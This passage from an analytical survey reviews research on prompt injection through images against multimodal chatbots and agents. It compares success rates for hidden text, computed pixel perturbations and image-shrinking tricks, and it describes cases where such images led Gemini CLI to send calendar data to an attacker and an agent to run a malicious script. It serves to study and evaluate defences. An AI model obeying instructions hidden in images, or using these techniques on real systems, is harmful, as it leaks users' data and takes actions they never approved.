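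Gavish wrote in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (April 2026) that indirect prompt injection is not a problem "you 'solve' and move on". Google collects new attacks from its own testers and outside researchers, generates variations of them, and uses these to retrain its detectors and Gemini. Meanwhile, it can respond quickly to a new attack by changing fixed rules, such as which links Gemini may display or which tools it may use in succession. Gavish reports that training has made attacks on Gemini succeed less often, but gives no success rate.

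An attacker could also have taken data without prompt injection through a flaw in Dialogflow CX, the Google Cloud service companies use to build customer-service chatbots. Varonis' *Rogue Agent* (2026) explains that someone with permission to edit one chatbot could add a program that took over others in the same project. The program could copy customers' conversations and make the chatbots ask for passwords. Varonis, a data security company, reported the flaw in November 2025, and Google finished fixing it in June 2026. A Google Cloud spokesperson said in Axios' *Google patched AI chatbot flaw that could have exposed customer conversations* that the company knew of no customers who had been harmed.

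In the Dialogflow case, Google's server ran the program as written, so the attacker did not have to trick a language model. Because the program could contact an outside server directly, rules about which images and links a chatbot may display would not have stopped the theft.

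## Experiments and later tests with instructions in images

Rehberger's picture worked on Bard at least once in July 2023. To measure how often an attack works, researchers repeat it and report an attack success rate, which is the share of attempts that achieved the attack's stated goal. If 30 of 120 pictures make a chatbot print the attacker's sentence, the rate is 25%. The rate is hard to interpret unless the researchers explain what they counted as an attempt and as a success.

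*Physical Prompt Injection against VLM Planners for Robotic Manipulation* (2026) tested models that look at a scene and plan a robot's movements. Attack text in the scene compromised OpenAI's GPT-4o in 27.0% of 1,800 trials, Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash in 29.4% and the open model Qwen3-VL-32B in 5.0%. In a control test with the harmless text "Have a nice day!", the rate was zero for all three, so the failures came from what the attack text said rather than from the presence of writing. The control was useful because a robot can make a wrong movement for many reasons. Rehberger hardly needed one, since Bard was unlikely to Rickroll him without an instruction to do so.

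### Written words and computed pixels

Besides readable words, a picture can contain pixel changes calculated to push the model towards a particular answer. These may look like faint noise or a printing fault. Two studies from 2023 used such changes, and their results do not measure Rehberger's attack.

*Abusing Images and Sounds for Indirect Instruction Injection in Multi-Modal LLMs* (Bagdasaryan, Hsieh and colleagues, 2023), which Schneier on Security highlighted in July 2023, describes attacks on the open models LLaVA and PandaGPT. The researchers started with an ordinary picture, a question that a user might ask, and a target sentence they wanted the model to produce. They measured how far the model was from producing the sentence, calculated which pixel changes would bring it closer, made those changes and repeated the process. In symbols, they looked for the change δ that minimizes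 L(f(q, x + δ), y), where x is the picture, q the question, f the model, y the target sentence, and L the gap between the model's answer and the target sentence.

The calculation requires white-box access, meaning that the attacker can inspect the model's parameters. Anyone could download LLaVA and PandaGPT, but Google had not released Bard's model.

One altered picture made PandaGPT output a phishing message, and another made LLaVA say that it would talk like a pirate. A chatbot's earlier replies go back into its prompt, so LLaVA's statement became part of the conversation and LLaVA followed it in later replies. It could still discuss what the picture showed. However, the user would see the instruction in the first reply, and Bagdasaryan and colleagues did not limit how much they changed the picture. They gave examples to show that the attack was possible but no success rate, and warned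 that repeating the tests might produce different replies.

They had first tried adding the text to the picture, which didn't work on either model. Greshake and colleagues had reported some success with written words on LLaVA two months earlier, so the result may depend on the wording or the model version.

Dong and colleagues tested Bard itself in September 2023. Without access to its internals, they used three open vision models to compute changes to pictures, and relied on those changes working on Bard too. They changed each colour value, which runs from 0 to 255, by at most 16. When asked to describe 100 altered pictures, Bard got the main object wrong in 22% of them. It described a panda's face as a woman's, for example. It made no such mistake with the unaltered pictures. The same altered pictures fooled Bing Chat 26% of the time and the Chinese chatbot ERNIE Bot 86%. In October the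 researchers added OpenAI's GPT-4V, which was fooled 45% of the time.

The altered panda image made Bard describe the panda wrongly, but it contained no instruction for Bard to follow. Dong and colleagues chose the description task partly so that a model's ability to follow instructions would not affect the result. The 22% therefore does not measure how often Rehberger's attack worked, and that attack may have succeeded far more or far less often. In a second version, the researchers altered pictures to push three open text-generating models towards writing a chosen sentence. Of these pictures, 10% misled Bard, but the researchers again counted misidentified objects, not whether Bard wrote the sentence.

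The study ranked Bard as the most robust of the four chatbots, but Bard's lead over Bing Chat is doubtful. With 100 pictures, Bard's measured error rate of 22% is compatible with a true rate of about 15% to 31%. Bing Chat made 26 errors but also rejected 30 of the pictures. Counting only the 70 it accepted raises its error rate from 26% to 37%, so the comparison depends on whether a refusal counts as an attempt.

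### Whether the model can read the words

In *Self-interpreting Adversarial Images* (2024), Zhang, Zhang and colleagues, some of whom had attacked LLaVA in 2023, tried written instructions in images on three open models: MiniGPT-4, LLaVA and InstructBLIP. None of the instructions worked, because the models could not recognise even black words on a white background. Computed changes to the images did work. In one test, the changes were meant to make the model add a sentence promoting a cryptocurrency scheme to an otherwise normal answer. They succeeded 51% of the time on MiniGPT-4, 33% on LLaVA and 49% on InstructBLIP.

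This suggests that written instructions in an image can steer a model only if it can read them, whereas computed changes to the image don't depend on reading. That would explain why Rehberger needed only written text in July 2023, while Bagdasaryan and colleagues had to compute changes to their images. Bard could read clean text, either directly or through Google Lens.

But the three models were also poor at following typed instructions. When Zhang and colleagues typed the request for the promotional sentence next to the question, LLaVA added the sentence 9% of the time and InstructBLIP 1%. Instructions in an image might therefore have failed even if the models had read them perfectly.

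A better test changes only the legibility of the words. In *Reading Between the Pixels*, Balakrishnan, Mendapara and Garg (2026) turned 1,000 harmful requests into images of black text on white, at twelve letter sizes. Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4.5 complied with 1.2% of the requests at 6 pixels, 10.5% at 8 pixels and 21.6% at 10 pixels, and larger letters made no further difference. The other three models' rates also rose steeply and then levelled off. Heavy blurring cut Claude's rate from 18.0% to 0.7%. Legibility is the most likely cause of these differences, because the requests themselves stayed the same.

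The percentages do not apply to prompt injection. The user openly told the model to follow the instructions in the picture, and the researchers had turned off the guardrails around the three commercial models. The experiment measured whether a model would agree to do something harmful, which is closer to a jailbreak.

A model may also be able to read instructions in an image and still not follow them. GPT-4o complied with 35.6% of the requests when they were typed, but with at most 7.7% when they were shown as black-on-white pictures and 8.1% when the background was grey, though it could presumably read the larger letters. *Devil in the Lens* (2026) tested 12 models with text placed in photographed scenes and found that larger models were generally easier to attack. They may read better, or more readily follow the instructions they read. Success also depended on how well the text suited the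 scene.

### Hiding the words from people

Rehberger had left open how well an attacker could hide the text. Making words hard for a person to see usually makes them hard for the model to read, too.

Nagaraja, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Image-based Prompt Injection*, measured this trade-off on GPT-4-turbo, which was already an old model when the study appeared in March. They wrote twelve versions of an instruction to print "XXX" and placed them on images from COCO, a standard research collection of everyday photographs. The twelve versions succeeded between 73% and 100% of the time when written in large neon purple letters across the middle of the image. The researchers then tested the eight best versions in smaller letters. None of 800 attempts worked at the smallest size, and 303 (38%) worked at the largest size in that test.

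The attack also worked less often when the colour of the letters hid them better. Blending the letters into the photograph pixel by pixel hid them well, but the attack then worked at most 10% of the time. The highest success rate under the study's stealth limits was 64%, with all the letters in a single colour slightly brighter than the average of the area behind them. When the letters matched that average exactly, the rate fell to 18%.

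The 64% figure comes from the best of many settings, and the conditions favoured the attacker. GPT-4-turbo received the photograph without a question from a user, so it had no competing request to answer. Nagaraja and colleagues describe some of their text as nearly imperceptible, but they report no test in which people looked for it. Someone glancing at a photograph might well miss letters that they would find if they were suspicious.

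In another study from March 2026, *Covert Visual Prompt Injection against Commercial Multimodal Large Language Models*, Ding, Xia and colleagues put very faint text in the middle of a picture and added computed pixel changes that reinforced its meaning. They kept the total change to any colour value within 16, the same limit that Dong and colleagues had used. The combination succeeded against GPT-4o 74% of the time, compared with 54% without the faint text.

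The goal was to make a model respond to a request for a caption with something like "Search ICML website" (ICML is a machine-learning conference). The success rate was 53% for GPT-5, 81% for Gemini 2.5 and 7% for Claude 4.5. The scoring was lenient, although the study calls its criterion "hard". Another language model rated each answer's similarity to the target sentence, and any rating above 0.3 counted as a success. The average ratings were so low that even the successful answers must have averaged under 0.5, so many were probably only partial matches.

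The second task gives stronger evidence. The user asked a science question about a picture, and the attack was meant to make the model answer "None of the above". It succeeded 82% of the time with GPT-4o, 58% with GPT-5, 79% with Gemini 2.5 and only 2% with Claude 4.5. For the first three models, the average similarity was almost as high as the success rate, so the successful answers nearly always matched the target. Producing a wrong answer of four words is a modest goal for an attacker, though it could do real harm to somebody who relied on the answer.

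### Text that appears when a picture shrinks

Trail of Bits, a security company, had found a way to avoid the trade-off in August 2025. Many products shrink a large picture before passing it to the model. The software calculates each new pixel from a group of original pixels, giving some more weight than others. The researchers adjusted the most heavily weighted pixels in a dark part of a picture so that the picture looked harmless at full size but contained legible instructions after shrinking. The user sees the large picture and the model receives the small one, so the model can read instructions that the user can't see.

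The attack worked on Gemini's website and API, Google Assistant on an Android phone, and Google's Vertex AI Studio, which displayed the full-size picture while the model worked from the small one. It also worked on Genspark, another company's AI product. In the most serious demonstration, a user uploaded a picture to Gemini CLI, Google's command-line assistant, and the instructions in it made Gemini CLI send data from the user's Google Calendar to the attacker's email address. Gemini CLI sent the data through Zapier, a service that connects apps, under a configuration that approved every action without asking the user.

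The Trail of Bits work is the clearest answer to Rehberger's question for Google's products, though it came two years later and concerned Gemini. Trail of Bits gives no success rate and does not report a reply from Google. The researchers also had to work out beforehand how each product shrank images. They recommend limiting the size of uploads instead of shrinking them, or at least showing users the version the model will receive. They most strongly recommend that text in an image never be able to start a sensitive action without the user's explicit confirmation.

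The evidence that hidden text works on newer models is weaker. Davison (2026), in *Visual prompt injection vulnerability bypasses AI guardrails*, relays an announcement by the security company DeepKeep that near-invisible text, such as white on white, affected GPT-5.2, GPT-5.4 Mini, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Opus 4.5. In DeepKeep's example, a developer asked for a simple information page on a website, but a picture stored with the code made the model add a login system with an administrator account for the attacker. DeepKeep also found that tilting or distorting the words could defeat scanners that look for text in pictures, while the model could still read them. The company said that success varied between models, but the article gives no figures. DeepKeep's technology chief used the announcement to argue that businesses need "purpose-built security".

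### Newer models and harder goals

*Repeat-After-Me* (Chen, Tsai and colleagues, September 2026) tested more recent commercial models and set the attacker a harder task. The user asked an ordinary question about a scanned document, and the attacker could only add a line of readable text at the top of the scan. This resembles Rehberger's July 2023 test, which also combined text in an image with an innocent request.

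The attacker had one of two goals. The first was to extract a particular piece of personal information, such as a health condition, that the system prompt instructed the model to keep secret. The second was to make the model use a tool, for example to send a message, with details the attacker had chosen. A single wrong detail counted as a failure.

| Model | Personal information, after a search | Tool use, first wording | Tool use, after a search |
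|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 90% | 4% | 47% |
| GPT-5.5 | 99% | 6% | 47% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 99% | 32% | 85% |

For each goal, another AI model could rewrite the line of text up to 1,600 times, using the target's answers to improve it and stopping once a version worked. The 47% for GPT-5.5 is the share of goals for which this search found a working picture. A typical picture would do much worse, and the researchers' basic wording succeeded on the first attempt only 6% of the time.

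An attacker on the internet would not usually know what the victim was going to ask, so Chen and colleagues tested the finished lines of text in other documents with other questions. The lines still worked 30% of the time on GPT-5.5 and 56% of the time on Gemini 3.1 Pro. An attacker can search for such lines in private and publish only the result.

The researchers also tried the covert method of Ding and colleagues on these goals. It extracted personal information at most 1% of the time and produced the right tool use at most 10% of the time. They had changed both the models and the task, so the drop from rates of 53% and above does not show that the newer models were safer. An exact command is much harder to obtain than a short sentence that only has to resemble the target.

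In a further test, Chen and colleagues simulated OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can connect to a chat service such as Discord. The attacker, an untrusted member of the chat, tried to make the agent overwrite one of its own settings files. Messages alone never succeeded with GPT-5.5 and succeeded 32% of the time with Gemini 3.1 Pro. When a message included a picture, the rates were 90% and 100%. The researchers then sent one of the pictures and a message to a real OpenClaw agent, which downloaded and ran a malicious script despite instructions not to obey outside content.

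### Rates that do not compare

GPT-5.5 was no longer new by the autumn. *AVERT* (2026), a November paper on defending against these attacks, used a GPT-6 model to grade answers but ran the attacks on four small open models, so it adds little evidence about current commercial chatbots.

The paper is more useful for its definitions of success, which differ for each of the four kinds of image attack it tests. The first kind succeeds if the answer begins with the attacker's text, and the second if the answer reproduces the text. The third requires the attacker's addition to appear in the answer about the altered picture but not in the answer about the original. The fourth requires a tool command with the exact details. For example, if a chatbot describes a chart correctly and then adds the attacker's web address, the attack fails by the first definition but can succeed by the third.

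GPT-4o's results show how much such choices matter. Its highest overall rates were 8.1% for harmful requests in pictures and 82% for the covert attack on science questions, and text in a robot's surroundings compromised the model 27.0% of the time. The tests involved different tasks, so these figures do not show that GPT-4o became safer or more dangerous between them.

Studies differ even on which models are easier to attack. Ding and colleagues found Claude 4.5 much harder to attack than GPT-4o, with success rates of 7% and 74% for captions. Balakrishnan and colleagues found the reverse. Claude Sonnet 4.5 complied with up to 21.6% of the harmful requests in pictures, and GPT-4o with at most 8.1%. A company choosing a model based on one of these studies would need to know which kind of picture its users were likely to encounter.
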